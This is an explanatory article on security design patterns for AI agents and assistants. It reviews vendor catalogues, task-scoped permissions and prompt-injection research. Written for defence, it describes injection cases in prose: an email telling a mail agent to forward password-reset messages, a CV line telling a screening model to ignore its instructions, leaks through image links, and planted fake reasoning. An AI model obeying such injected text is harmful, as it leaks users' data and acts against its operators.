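# Security design patterns for AI workloads

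## What a security pattern for an AI workload is

A security pattern for an AI workload is a named, reusable solution to a recurring security problem in systems built around AI models. It includes a description of the situation the solution suits and its drawbacks. Software engineering borrowed the pattern format from building architecture, and much of the security thinking in these patterns is older than language models. The newer element is the central model, which reads text written by strangers and, in many systems, determines what the software does next.

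An AI workload is any running system built around such a model. One example is a company assistant that answers staff questions about their email and files. Anyone able to alter the data used to train its model could alter the model's behaviour. To answer a question, the assistant searches a retrieval store, which is an index of company documents, and adds the passages it finds to the model's input. It also has tools, which are ordinary software functions such as "search the mailbox" or "send a message". The tools log in to other systems with credentials, which are passwords, keys or access tokens. Logs record the inputs, the outputs and each use of a tool. They help investigators after an incident, but they also hold a second copy of any confidential text that passed through. An attacker can target any of these parts, and securing the training data does not protect the credentials.

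### From buildings to software security

In 1977 the architect Christopher Alexander and his co-authors published *A Pattern Language*, a book of 253 patterns ranging in scale from regions to doorknobs. A pattern in the book pairs a problem that keeps coming up in buildings and towns with the essentials of a solution, which builders adapt to their own site. In *Security patterns*, Howard, Curzi and Gantenbein (2023) open their chapter on Microsoft's Azure cloud with that definition. Alexander's group called all the patterns hypotheses and used asterisks to show their confidence in each, a practice software engineers adopted less readily than the pattern format itself.

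Erich Gamma, Richard Helm, Ralph Johnson and John Vlissides brought the idea to programming with *Design Patterns* (1994), which describes 23 ways of arranging the parts of a program. Yoder and Barcalow (1997) described seven security patterns in *Architectural Patterns for Enabling Application Security*. They had learned how hard it is to add security late by reworking a finished financial application to meet corporate security requirements. Their Single Access Point pattern sends every user through a single login, because one entrance is easier to guard than many, as at a military base. They also note the drawback that the application loses the convenience of several entrances. Later collections include *Security Patterns Repository Version 1.0*, with 26 patterns for web applications, and the book *Security patterns* by Schumacher, Fernandez-Buglioni and colleagues (2006).

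Researchers wrote patterns much faster than they tested them. Javan Jafari and Rasoolzadegan (2018), in *Security Patterns*, sorted 274 papers from 1997 to 2017 and found that 52% developed or organised patterns while 8% evaluated them, mostly by qualitative methods such as expert judgement. Most of the empirical evaluations they reviewed favoured patterns. *Do security patterns really help designers?* (2015) is an exception. It compared 32 teams of master's students designing a banking system with and without security patterns, and detected no difference in the security of the designs or in the teams' productivity, though the teams preferred having the patterns. A sample of that size could easily miss a modest benefit, so the result is not conclusive, but it is a reason not to treat designers' liking for a catalogue (a published collection of patterns in a common form) as evidence that the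 catalogue makes systems safer.

Microsoft and others now publish catalogues of patterns in the same form for AI workloads. *From Goals to Aspects, Revisited* (Yu, 2026) presents twelve patterns for software agents, including four for problems that earlier collections had no reason to cover.

### The standard form and a worked entry

*What is a Design Pattern?*, a set of UBC lecture slides, lists the four elements that Gamma's group considered essential: name, problem, solution and consequences. Templates have since grown, and the one published by the Hillside Group, the organisation behind the PLoP conferences on patterns, adds context, forces (considerations that pull a designer in different directions), known uses and related patterns. Six fields are enough for a small example, an assistant that can read a mailbox but not change anything in it.

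| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Name | Read-only assistant |
| Context | Staff ask an AI assistant questions about their own email. Outsiders can put text in front of the model simply by writing to a member of staff. |
| Problem | A message may contain instructions aimed at the model. If the assistant can send, forward or delete mail, an attacker may get it to do so. |
| Solution | Give the assistant a credential that the mail server accepts for searching and reading only. Connect no tool that sends, forwards or deletes. Display answers as plain text, without clickable links or images. |
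| Consequences | No message can make the assistant send or delete mail. Staff have to send their own replies. A hostile message can still distort a summary, and the assistant can still read the whole mailbox. |
| Related patterns | Permissions that change with the task, for assistants that must sometimes write; human approval before sending; a log of every use of a tool. |

The pattern fails without the line about links and images, because a web address can carry data. If the user's screen loads an image from an attacker's server, the image's address can contain text copied from the mailbox, so an assistant can leak mail even without a sending tool. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) warns about embedded links for this reason. Advice to "restrict the assistant's permissions" would not have prevented such a leak.

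The consequences field is the one a designer most needs when choosing between patterns, and the easiest to leave thin. Yu's entry for the Tool Scope Sandbox pattern, which checks each file path, command and web domain against a list of permitted ones, rates the pattern strongly positive for security and safety but negative for capability. Yu also states that a check of who is asking must come first, and lists which other patterns combine well with the sandbox. The evidence behind the collection is narrower. Yu's case study measures how widely such checks are scattered across the 192 files of one open-source agent framework, which bears on how maintainable the code is and only indirectly on whether an attack would succeed.

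### Principles, controls and threat lists

The read-only assistant applies the principle of least privilege, one of eight design principles in Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). Programs and users should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job", as stated on the page that Levchenko (2017) reproduces in *Principles* for a university security course. Saltzer and Schroeder argued that this limits the damage from an accident or error and leaves auditors fewer programs to examine when someone suspects misuse of a privilege.

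The principle applies to a payroll database as well as to an AI assistant, but it is so general that the designer must still decide which component enforces the limit and which privileges the job requires, even though the job changes with every sentence the user types. The pattern specifies both for one context. The assistant may only read mail, and the mail server enforces that limit whatever text the model produces. Two more of the 1975 principles come up constantly in work on AI agents. Fail-safe defaults means refusing access unless a rule permits it, so an agent's list of tools should start empty. Complete mediation means checking every access, so checking only at login is not enough for an agent that then takes forty actions.

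A control is narrower than a pattern: it is a checklist requirement that an auditor can mark as met or unmet, such as "the assistant's mail credential permits reading only". TS 104 223, published by the European standards body ETSI, is a baseline of such security requirements for AI systems. Controls are useful for comparing suppliers and catching omissions. They usually omit the reasoning behind them, so a team that meets a control may not know what staff lose by it or when a different design would work better.

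Threat lists describe what can go wrong but don't specify how to design the system. OWASP, a non-profit that works on software security, ranks the main risks to applications built on language models in its Top 10, and MITRE ATLAS catalogues the techniques that attackers use against AI systems. A document with "pattern" in its title may not describe a security pattern, since some authors also write up attacks as patterns. Javan Jafari and Rasoolzadegan call these misuse patterns and consider them the opposite of security patterns. Each one describes the steps of an attack and identifies the security patterns that counter it.

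### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

OWASP's list puts prompt injection first, and many of the newer patterns exist because of it. The attack is easiest to follow in a single run of an agent, which is a language model that chooses actions and carries them out with tools over several steps.

Suppose an assistant can read and send mail, and a user asks it to summarise the week's messages from suppliers. The surrounding software builds a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, a description of each available tool, and the user's request. The model continues this text. If its continuation is a tool call, a structured request such as "search mail, sender: suppliers, period: seven days", the software runs the search with the assistant's credentials, adds the results to the prompt, and calls the model again. This loop repeats until the model writes a final answer. Only ordinary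 code accesses the mailbox, so that code can also block the model's requests.

One supplier's message in the search results contains a line telling the assistant to forward all recent password-reset emails to an outside address. The model's prompt now contains two requests, and its next output may be a tool call that forwards the mail. The software runs the call because it is well formed and comes from an authorised agent. This is prompt injection, the use of text to make a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of those of its user or operator. The attacker needed no password, only a way to get untrusted content into the prompt. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter's system that scores CVs, in which a candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore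 its earlier instructions and approve the application.

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form and a careless program passes them to the database, which executes them. Parameterised queries fix this by sending the command and the user's data separately, so the database never interprets the data as a command. Language models have no such separate channel. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) represents this as F(p‖d), where the model F receives the developer's prompt p and the data d joined as one string. David C argues that because the model only predicts the next token (a word or a piece of one), prompt injection may never have a complete fix like the one for SQL injection.

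Developers try to mark the boundary by wrapping each stretch of text in markers that label it as coming from the system, the user or a tool, and by training models to give some labels more authority than others. This helps, though *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) judges that such labels are not a hard security boundary. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) offer the explanation that a text's style can override its label. They wrapped identical passages of web text in the markers for different roles and trained a simple classifier to recognise, from the model's internal activity, which marker was present. Since the passages were the same, the classifier could learn only the effect of the markers. They then applied it to a conversation in which every line carried the user's marker, including lines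 written in the style of the model's own reasoning. The classifier still overwhelmingly identified the reasoning-style lines as the model's reasoning.

The same team turned the finding into an attack by planting fake reasoning in web pages and user messages. Absurd justifications worked about as well as plausible ones. Rewording the fake reasoning to remove its characteristic style, while keeping the argument, cut the success rate to about a sixth. These models, which date from 2025, largely treated text that sounded like a trusted speaker as if that speaker had written it. Newer models may resist this particular trick.

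Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, ask whether better training could ever close the gap completely. A model converts each token into a list of numbers, and the word "write" becomes the same list whether the developer or an attacker typed it. Suppose an ideal observer sees one internal representation and has to say whether it came from trusted or untrusted text, each equally likely beforehand. The observer's lowest possible error rate is

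error = ½ × (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two distributions of representations lie. It is 0 when they are identical and 1 when they do not overlap at all. At a TV of 0.9 the best observer still errs 5% of the time. Two further steps complete the argument. The model's attention mechanism blends information from all positions in the prompt, so untrusted text contributes to the very computation that produces a tool call. And training covers finitely many examples, while an attacker has unlimited ways to encode the same message.

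The impossibility proof has a limited scope. The overlap is obvious for single tokens, but Pant and colleagues assume it, rather than derive it, for a model's deeper layers, which also take in position and surrounding text. Measurements by Ye and colleagues make that assumption plausible. The property that the proof rules out is also modest. It requires decisions about tools to depend on what untrusted text means and never on how an attacker encodes it. A model could have that property and still obey a plainly worded instruction in an email. The lack of a guarantee also does not determine how often attacks succeed, and training can reduce that rate.

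The theorem does not apply where a mechanism outside the model decides whether a tool call may run, and this exception is what matters most for design. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues reach the same conclusion from engineering, sorting defences by where they act. Training and careful prompting act on the model and give no guarantees. Confirmation prompts rely on the user, and tired users approve unsafe actions. Controls in the surrounding system can hold even when an attack manipulates the model. Their rule for such systems is that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger a consequential action, and they apply this rule in six designs.

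### Attack success rate and utility

Tests of these defences mainly use two measures. Attack success rate is the share of attack attempts that achieve the attacker's goal, and utility is the share of legitimate tasks the system completes. Either measure alone is almost useless for judging a defence, because it can be made to look excellent by giving up the other. For example, an agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of 0% but completes no legitimate tasks. An agent with every permission and no checks may complete nearly all its legitimate tasks, but also the attacker's.

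The read-only assistant shows how utility and attack success rate interact. If 80 of 100 staff requests need only reading and 20 end in sending a reply, removing the sending tool caps utility at 80%, however good the model. Attacks that aim to send mail from the account then always fail, even when the attacker is more skilled, because there is no tool to call. But the pattern does nothing to stop an attack that aims to put a false payment date into a summary. An attack success rate therefore applies only to a particular goal, and a benchmark full of email-sending attacks would make this design look more secure than it is.

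A test result also applies only to the kind of attacker tested. A static test replays a fixed set of attacks, while an adaptive attacker watches how the defended system responds and revises the attack. Ye and colleagues cite earlier work in which human testers and adaptive attacks almost always defeated models with near-perfect scores on injection benchmarks. A larger collection of attacks doesn't solve this problem if the attacks are similar. Zorz (2026) reports in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands of times* that training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack, and that a large set of attacks may be one attack repeated.

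Small attack success rates also add up over repeated attempts. If each attempt succeeds 1% of the time and attempts are independent, an attacker who sends 100 messages has a 63% chance of at least one success. Real attempts are not independent, since an attacker learns from failures and a defender may notice them, but the calculation shows why a rate that would be acceptable for a spam filter can be alarming for an agent that holds the company's credentials.

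An agent's measured utility may differ sharply depending on whether it is tested with or without an attack under way. An agent that halts whenever it detects an injection will have a low attack success rate and full utility when tested without an attack, but anyone who can send it an email can stop it from working by including an injection.

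## The published catalogues and how their entries are written

Four of the six main publishers of security guidance for AI workloads are companies that sell the platforms or security products the guidance applies to. The other two are an industry coalition and a long-running project for security architects. None of the six supports its AI entries with results from attacks on systems that follow them. They rely mostly on experience instead, and Microsoft is the most explicit about doing so.

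Microsoft began its Secure Future Initiative, a company-wide security programme, in November 2023, and says it has put the equivalent of more than 34,000 engineers on it. In August 2025 it opened a public library of what they had learned. Microsoft's launch announcement, *Sharing practical guidance*, gives every entry five fields: a name, the problem, the solution (what Microsoft did internally), guidance for customers, and the implications (benefits and trade-offs). The solution field gives readers something to check. For example, the entry on legacy systems is based on Microsoft's removal of more than 5.75 million inactive tenants (organisations' separate areas in its cloud). Removing that many shows that the measure is workable at scale, but the figure doesn't measure how many attacks it prevented.

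The eight launch entries covered ordinary enterprise security, such as phishing-resistant login and log retention. None dealt with securing AI, and entries on agents came later. Microsoft's *Explore actionable patterns and practices from the Secure Future Initiative (SFI)* now presents the whole library as based on "tested security insights".

Other publishers use the word "pattern" for different things. In Cisco's *AI security reference architectures*, a design pattern is a type of application, such as a single-purpose chatbot or a model connected to a document database, and the security advice follows as threats and mitigations. Amazon Web Services (AWS) uses the word for ways of arranging agents, which Sempf and Hooker (2025) call "foundational blueprints" in *Agentic AI patterns and workflows on AWS*. The AWS security guide is a numbered list of practices, each marked as AI-specific or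 general. NVIDIA's *Agent Blueprint Patterns* are templates for seven workplace assistants. The five patterns in Open Security Architecture's *OSA AI Security Suite* are closer to whole security programmes, and the Coalition for Secure AI (2025) offers three principles.

| Publisher | What an entry is | Main readers | Basis offered |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft | A risk area, with problem, solution, guidance and outcomes | Customers and security practitioners | The company's internal experience |
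| Open Security Architecture | A set of controls, with context, roles and limits | A different role for most entries | Published threat lists, laws and control standards |
| AWS | A numbered practice | Teams building agents on AWS | Operating experience and AWS's general design framework |
| Cisco | A type of application, with its threats and mitigations | Developers of language-model applications | Reasoning, with some cited research |
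| NVIDIA | An assistant, with its goal, usual services and review gate | Organisations deploying assistants, including regulated ones | Reasoning about leaks, accountability and regulation |
| Coalition for Secure AI | A principle, with a rationale and suggested practices | Agent developers, adopters and security engineers | Industry experience, stated in general terms |

### One Microsoft entry, field by field

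The library's main entry on agents is Microsoft's *Reduce autonomous agentic AI system risk*. The name is of little use in a design discussion because it states only an aim, and almost any security measure reduces risk. An engineer can tell roughly what to build from names such as "Single Access Point" and "read-only assistant".

The problem field covers eight risks. Four concern design: agents that stray from the task, too little human control, behaviour that users cannot see, and people not knowing they are dealing with an AI. The other four are agent hijacking, leaks of sensitive data, compromised suppliers, and "agent sprawl", the spread of agents that nobody manages or that hold too many permissions. Microsoft correctly attributes hijacking to blurred boundaries between data and instructions. But eight problems are a lot for one pattern, and Microsoft applies its foundational advice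 to every use of agents, so designers can't learn from the entry when another pattern would fit better.

According to the launch announcement, the "solution" part of an entry would describe what Microsoft did. This entry instead gives 35 instructions under eight headings, and one of them, to inventory all models, tools, plugins and data sources, appears word for word under both supply chain compromise and agent sprawl. The instructions vary greatly in how much they leave the engineer to decide. One way to see this is to imagine giving the same instruction to two engineers who cannot consult each other, each building a version of the previous section's mailbox assistant that may also send mail.

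| Instruction, in paraphrase | What the two engineers would probably build |
|---|---|
| Give every agent a unique, auditable identity | Nearly the same thing: a separate account for the assistant, with its name on every log line |
| Allow only listed tools, and check their parameters with fixed rules | The same mechanism, with different lists and rules |
| Keep logs of actions, tools and outcomes | Similar logs, though one might store the text of the emails and the other might not |
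| Require approval for high-risk or irreversible actions | One asks before every message, the other only before mail to outside addresses |
| Strictly separate instructions, data, memory and tool parameters | Different systems: one adds markers to the prompt, the other splits the work between two models |
| Ground behaviour in explicit rules, not inferred intent | No common design, and possibly just a longer prompt |

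An auditor could check the instructions in the top three rows, and could also check the approval rule once someone lists the actions it covers, which Microsoft leaves to the reader. Strict separation is the hardest to act on because it requires a property that language models lack. Achieving it takes a different architecture, such as one of the six designs by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, but the entry does not direct readers to one. The entry's best design rule is to block prohibited actions with deterministic controls, which puts the check in fixed code that gives the same answer whatever the model outputs.

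The guidance field is a table of seven recommendations, each with a resource. Five of the resources belong to Foundry, Microsoft's platform for building AI applications, or Entra, its identity service. The other two are Microsoft's model of how customers and providers share responsibility and its toolkit for designing user interfaces. For agent identity, which covers least privilege, isolation, lifecycle management and auditing, the resource is Entra Agent ID. This saves time for companies already on Microsoft's cloud, which get a working component along with the advice, but companies on other clouds get four goals and no description of what a substitute product would have to do. Even for Microsoft's customers, some resources only partly match the recommendations. For dependencies, the recommendation is to keep an inventory of models, tools, plugins and data sources, but the resource is a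 catalogue of models.

Microsoft's last field, "outcomes", lists benefits as though adopting the pattern guaranteed them, including that agents "execute only within defined intent, permissions, and boundaries". The trade-offs take three lines: extra engineering work, the complexity of systems with several agents, and possible friction for users. The second comes from using several agents, with or without the pattern. The field omits the drawbacks a designer would most want to estimate, such as the share of legitimate tasks the agent can no longer finish and the number of approvals staff must give each day. The "key success factors" restate the solution as a finished state, for instance that controls reliably block prohibited actions. A more usable success factor for the mailbox assistant would be that the mail server refuses all 200 messages when testers request 200 to unapproved addresses.

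### How specific the other entries are

NVIDIA's blueprints are shorter and more specific. The "knowledge worker assistant" searches mail, chat, documents and tickets, and a person must review its work before it sends, forwards, publishes or deletes anything. This is specific enough that two engineers would put the review gate in the same place. For code, NVIDIA also specifies how the review works. The agent writes to its own branch, a separate copy of the code, and proposes a merge, which a person accepts or rejects. NVIDIA requires review because writing is one of the two channels through which an agent can leak data (the other is outbound traffic), approved writes are often hard to undo, a named reviewer makes someone accountable, and regulated industries already require human review of consequential actions. NVIDIA wants each blueprint to specify its tools, data scope, write permissions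 and logging, but the published table gives only the goal, the typical services and the gate.

NVIDIA also does not discuss how well reviewers review, and the publishers disagree about when human review is needed. The Coalition for Secure AI warns that over-reliance on human intervention leads to "control fatigue" and can turn a safeguard into security theatre. It recommends that people set boundaries and thresholds and step in only for high-risk or unusual events. NVIDIA requires approval for every write to a system of record. The better approach probably depends on volume. Programmers already review merges, so a coding agent adds to an existing queue, but an assistant that drafts 500 customer replies a day would create a new queue that nobody could read with care. A good consequences field would describe how much review work a pattern creates at different volumes.

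An entry can give precise instructions for a weak defence. Cisco passes on a technique called spotlighting, in which the software replaces every space in a retrieved document with a special character and the prompt tells the model never to obey text marked that way. Cisco includes the one line of code needed, so two engineers would implement it the same way. But the technique carries no guarantee, because it works by influencing the model. Cisco calls a secure prompt only a good first step.

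Other Cisco entries show the weakness of filling in a form threat by threat. Cisco lists input filtering as a mitigation for six of the thirteen threats to agents. The only mitigation listed for interception of data in transit is to update and patch storage systems, and the same sentence appears under unauthorised access to a chatbot's memory. Encrypted connections, the usual remedy for interception, appear in a different part of the page. Cisco also recommends "real-time AI protection" in its diagrams, and the page ends with a link to Cisco AI Defense, a product it sells for that purpose.

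The Coalition's principles are higher-level and cover what an organisation should decide before it designs anything. Under them, agentic systems should be governed by accountable people, bounded and resilient, and transparent and verifiable. Some of the more detailed advice is useful in practice, such as choosing in advance whether a failing agent should halt, fall back to a few predictable functions, or stop quickly before an error spreads. Other lines, such as the one on using automated policy enforcement to "bound non-determinism in real-time", are so vague that two engineers following them would build entirely different things.

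### Where one pattern stops and the next begins

Open Security Architecture has described problems with its first attempt to divide AI security into patterns. In February 2026 it published Secure AI Integration, its first new pattern in over a decade. It then compared its AI patterns with four outside frameworks: MITRE ATLAS, the EU AI Act, the threat landscape of the EU's cybersecurity agency ENISA, and the AI risk management framework of NIST, the US standards institute. It found overlaps, blind spots and no clear reading order. Seven topics each appeared in two or three patterns: prompt injection, shadow AI (tools that staff use without approval), human oversight, trust between agents, the model supply chain, persistent memory and audit logging.

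Open Security Architecture decided that it had divided its AI patterns in the wrong way, and reorganised them by the questions different readers have. Secure AI Integration covers running a single agent. Secure Agentic AI Frameworks is for the security architect whose company wants a platform for running many agents, and AI Governance and Responsible AI is for the executives, lawyers and risk staff who decide what the company may deploy. Of the remaining two, one covers attacks made with AI, such as cloned voices and deepfaked executives, and the other covers the AI tools that security teams use, which an attacker might mislead with specially written log entries. An architect starting a new programme should read the governance pattern first, then the single-agent pattern, then the one on frameworks.

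The argument for five patterns instead of one is convincing, because lawyers and detection engineers need different things. The new division still leaves some overlap, since prompt injection defences and audit logs belong to both the single-agent pattern and the frameworks pattern, and both patterns seem to need them. This kind of gap analysis can also only find missing or repeated topics, so a control that any competent attacker could defeat would still pass if it appeared once and in the right place.

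The entries in *Secure Agentic AI Frameworks*, by Aurelius and Vitruvius, are fuller than Microsoft's. The paper ties its advice to 35 controls from NIST's standard list, SP 800-53, so a company that already audits against that list can see which of its existing checks apply. It explains when not to use the pattern, for example when a company uses only ready-made AI services whose provider runs the agents. It also divides each control area among developers, architects and business owners, arguing that if the business owner does not define what an agent may do alone, the developer "will default to maximum autonomy because it is easier to build". Several of its rules pass the two-engineer test. For example, an agent that can only read files cannot start a helper agent that can write them, and an agent that uses three times its expected token budget triggers an investigation.

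The entry's threat-resistance field claims much more than this supports. Aurelius and Vitruvius write that layered guardrails with adversarial testing ensure that injected text "cannot redirect the agent's objective". They cite no test, and no filter on a model's input or output can guarantee that. They also claim that the entry addresses 463 attack techniques. That number counts the items on MITRE's ATT&CK list that the 35 controls relate to, and it would stay the same if a company implemented every control badly.

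### Patterns tied to goals and code

Yu's pattern language, the academic collection of twelve patterns, is meant to narrow the gap between goals and implementation. Each entry has a problem, a goal model, a solution in the programming language Rust, and notes on which patterns it needs or combines with. A goal model is a diagram that links the agent's required functions, such as running a tool, to qualities it should have, such as security or low cost. Yu draws each link as a V, with the function at the top left, the quality at the top right, and a task that affects both at the bottom. The crosscutting density of a task t, written δ(t), is the number of qualities it affects. Calling the language model has δ = 4, because the call may carry an injection, costs money, can fail, and must be recorded. The code therefore needs four separate checks at that point.

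The code half of a pattern is an aspect, which a programmer writes once and the compiler attaches to many functions, to run before, after or around them. When several aspects share a function, their order matters. Yu puts identity first so that a caller without permission never uses up the budget. The limits on tools, the scan for injections, the rate limit and the spending limit follow in that order, with logging and auditing near the end.

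Eight of the twelve patterns adapt familiar ones, such as the circuit breaker, which stops calls to a failing service. The four new ones are the Tool Scope Sandbox, a Prompt Guard that scans inputs for known injection phrasings, a Token Budget that cuts off an agent that has used up its allowance, and an Action Audit Trail. Even here, some of the printed code is incomplete. The sandbox listing has two comments in place of the check. The audit trail is supposed to record why an agent acted, but its listing stores only the time, the session, the function's name and whether the call was starting or had failed. Yu provides implementations separately.

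The testing concerns maintainability. Yu examined four versions of ZeroClaw, an open-source agent framework that grew from 91 to 200 files within a week in February 2026. Its programmers had written rate limiting three times, with different error formats, and had written the check that keeps an agent inside its own folder in three different ways. A fix to one version of that check could easily miss the others, which is a security argument for writing it once. Yu then rebuilt the rate limiting for eight functions, replacing about 195 lines with eight one-line annotations. Part of the saving comes from using an existing library that already contained the rate limiter.

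Yu reports that some of the study's counts are unreliable. Yu found the scattered checks by keyword search, then inspected samples by hand. For security and authorisation, 80% of the matches were correct, but for path validation only 32% were, which reduces an apparent 68 files to about 22. Yu also classes prompt injection defence as absent from ZeroClaw, while noting that the fourth version added some. No one tested the framework against attacks before or after that change. The Prompt Guard looks for known phrasings, so an attacker could evade it by rewording a message.

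### Shared vocabulary or renamed checklist

Catalogues are meant to give engineers common names, save them from solving the same problem twice, and give reviewers something to check a design against. The names are the weakest part so far, since a "pattern" may be a risk area, a control programme, a type of chatbot or a few lines of Rust. The Coalition for Secure AI was still calling for a common language in 2025. The publishers agree more on substance. Microsoft, AWS, NVIDIA and Open Security Architecture all want the decisive checks outside the model, in ordinary code or infrastructure. This fits what researchers know about prompt injection, but the four recommendations are not independent evidence, because the publishers read many of the same threat lists.

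Designers can already reuse specific entries, and reviewers can check systems against them. For example, the rule that a helper agent never gains permissions its parent lacks can go into a new system unchanged. A reviewer with NVIDIA's table can ask whether the assistant can forward a message before someone approves it, and expect a yes or no answer.

One objection is that many entries are old checklists with the word "agent" added. AWS's own labels partly support this. In the sections of its guide on development, input validation, data and incident response, AWS marks nine practices as AI-specific and ten as general. The general ones include code review, data loss prevention, and emergency shutdown and continuity plans. But the labels are themselves uncertain. AWS counts threat modelling, which long predates language models, as AI-specific, and counts removing phrases that tell a model to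 ignore its instructions as general. One of the AI-specific practices for input validation is to deploy Amazon Bedrock Guardrails, which is closer to buying a product than applying a design pattern, though AWS also advises adding other layers.

AWS's *Four security principles for agentic AI systems*, a summary of the company's response to a request for information that NIST issued in January 2026, argues that agents need no new security paradigm. Attackers still steal credentials and exploit careless code, and an agent with excessive privileges can do more damage, faster, than a person with the same access. Two of the four principles therefore continue existing practice. The two that AWS considers new are to enforce limits outside the model and to grant an agent autonomy one type of operation at a time, based on a record of what it recommended, what a person decided and what happened. In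 its guide, AWS says that the agent's reasoning is what is new and that conventional security largely covers the agent's inputs and actions. This overstates how well conventional security covers inputs, because they can carry prompt injection, which AWS itself lists as an input risk.

A critic can accept that the old controls still matter but object to calling them patterns. A checklist helps a team notice that it has no shutdown procedure, but it doesn't help the team choose between an assistant that only reads mail and one that sends mail after approval. That choice depends on context and drawbacks, the fields these catalogues fill in least. Judged by whether they help with such choices, Microsoft's entry on agents is mostly a checklist, while NVIDIA's blueprints and the better rules from Open Security Architecture are patterns, if brief ones.

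It is unclear whether the difference affects security. The 2015 experiment with master's students found no gain from patterns for older software, and incidents in deployed systems give only indirect evidence about catalogues. None of these publishers reports having run a direct trial, though one would not be complicated. Some teams would build an agent from a full catalogue entry, others would build one from a bare list of the same controls, and the same attackers would try to break into both groups' agents.

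## Limiting an agent's permissions to its task

Most of the catalogues recommend giving an agent only the access it needs, but few explain how to determine what that is. The read-only mail assistant was an easy case because it did one kind of work. A support agent may answer a billing question, issue a refund and correct an address in one morning, and each task needs different access. Developers usually give the agent all the access it might need. These standing permissions remain available during every task, so an attacker who hijacks the agent while it is correcting an address can also issue refunds.

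Excess permissions were common before AI agents. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites one vendor's analysis in which accounts across several cloud platforms used only 1% of their permissions. It also cites a study in which 99.8% of 447,000 GitHub workflows, the scripts that build and test code automatically, had more access than they needed. This mostly does companies no harm because people and scripts rarely use the excess. But agents choose their own tools, and across 544 scenarios, six of eleven models chose a more privileged tool than the task required in over 30% of cases.

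One approach is to change how the agent chooses tools. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (2026) tests a prompt that instructs the agent to prefer the least privileged tool and to retry it before moving to a stronger one. It also trains models to use the stronger tool only as a last resort. Both methods may reduce accidents, but neither guarantees protection against an attacker, because both depend on the model's behavior. The alternative is to remove the agent's permission to use the stronger tool for the length of the task.

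### From identity to revocation

Permission scoping means limiting what an agent can access and do to what its role or current task needs. The first step is to give the agent its own account. Suppose an employee asks a company's support agent to "refund order 4417 and email the customer a receipt". If the agent logs in as that employee, it can open everything the employee can, and the logs won't show which of them issued the refund. The logs should identify both the agent and the employee. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes a draft standard, AIMS, that treats agents as software with delegated authority and keeps the user's identity attached for audits.

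*Access Control for Agentic AI* (Wei and Xiong, 2026) cites a measurement of 7,973 live servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. About 41% of them offered their tools without any login. Official guidance is still at an early stage. In February 2026, NIST published a draft concept paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher et al., 2026), which drew over 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026).

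The company then sets a ceiling for the agent's role, which is the most permissions it may ever have. Support agents might be able to read orders, refund up to $200 and email customers, but never open payroll. A ceiling is easy to enforce, and instructions in an email can't change it. But it has to cover everything the role ever does, so it allows more than any single task needs.

Next, the system works out what this task needs: reading order 4417, refunding that order, and sending one message to the address on it. *Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (2025) separates the actions an agent may take from the resources it may use, and recommends translating the plain-language request into structured permissions that people can review and software can enforce. This is the hardest step. *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (2026) points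 out that a fixed list of permissions can withhold access the task needs while granting unrelated sensitive access.

The agent then receives a credential that covers only those permissions and expires after a few minutes. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes a stricter version, in which a separate service called a custodian holds the credential, checks each request against the granted permissions and carries out the operation itself. The agent never sees the credential, so it can't leak it. If the agent hands part of the work to a helper, it can pass on a narrower credential. Some token formats, such as Macaroons, let the holder add restrictions but not remove them. A helper that drafts the receipt could get a token that only allows reading order 4417.

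When the refund has gone through, the system revokes the credential, with the expiry time as a fallback. Revocation is harder when several agents share a helper, because cutting the helper off for one task may break another. VERA, a system in the same survey, handles this by recording who authorised whom and letting the helper keep its access as long as one independent chain of authorisation remains valid. Wei and Xiong note that revocation can stop new actions and sometimes cancel pending ones, but it can't undo completed actions such as sending an email.

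### Why a task is easier to scope than a job

Companies give employees permissions by role because setting them for each task would take too much work. Someone would have to learn what each employee was about to do, decide what access that required, and change the settings several times a day. Employees also get many of their tasks in conversation or plan them without writing them down, so no system could read those tasks in advance.

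An agent receives its task as text before it acts, so software can read the text, predict which permissions the task needs, and issue them in less time than the agent takes to produce its first sentence. This removes most of the overhead that made task-by-task access impractical for people.

Text also has a weakness here, because it describes a goal rather than a list of operations. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* gives the example "Triage these tickets", which could involve reading, tagging, closing or forwarding them, so the system has to infer which operations to allow. An attacker who can write part of the text can influence the permissions. The system should therefore derive them from the user's own words before the agent reads anything else, though users often paste in text that other people wrote.

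### A test on 600 tasks

*Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) measured how well limiting an agent's permissions to its task works for an imaginary company with six departments. It used 600 tasks written by a language model, each labelled with the permissions it needs from a list of 15, such as reading the database or sending email outside the company. People checked 60 of the labels for Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*, the workshop paper that introduced the dataset. Agreement was high (Cohen's kappa of 0.967, where 1 is perfect), but it was measured after the reviewers had settled disagreements.

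An agent gets a permission only if three layers allow it. A role ceiling lists the permissions that each department's agents may ever hold. A task classifier, a small language model trained on 500 of the 600 tasks, predicts which permissions a task needs from its description. Then a set of prohibitions removes permissions that are risky in combination. For example, an agent that can both read the database and make web requests could copy records to an outside server, so a rule removes the permission to make web requests unless the agent works for the data and analytics department, whose job requires both. Noyan tested the system on the remaining 100 tasks.

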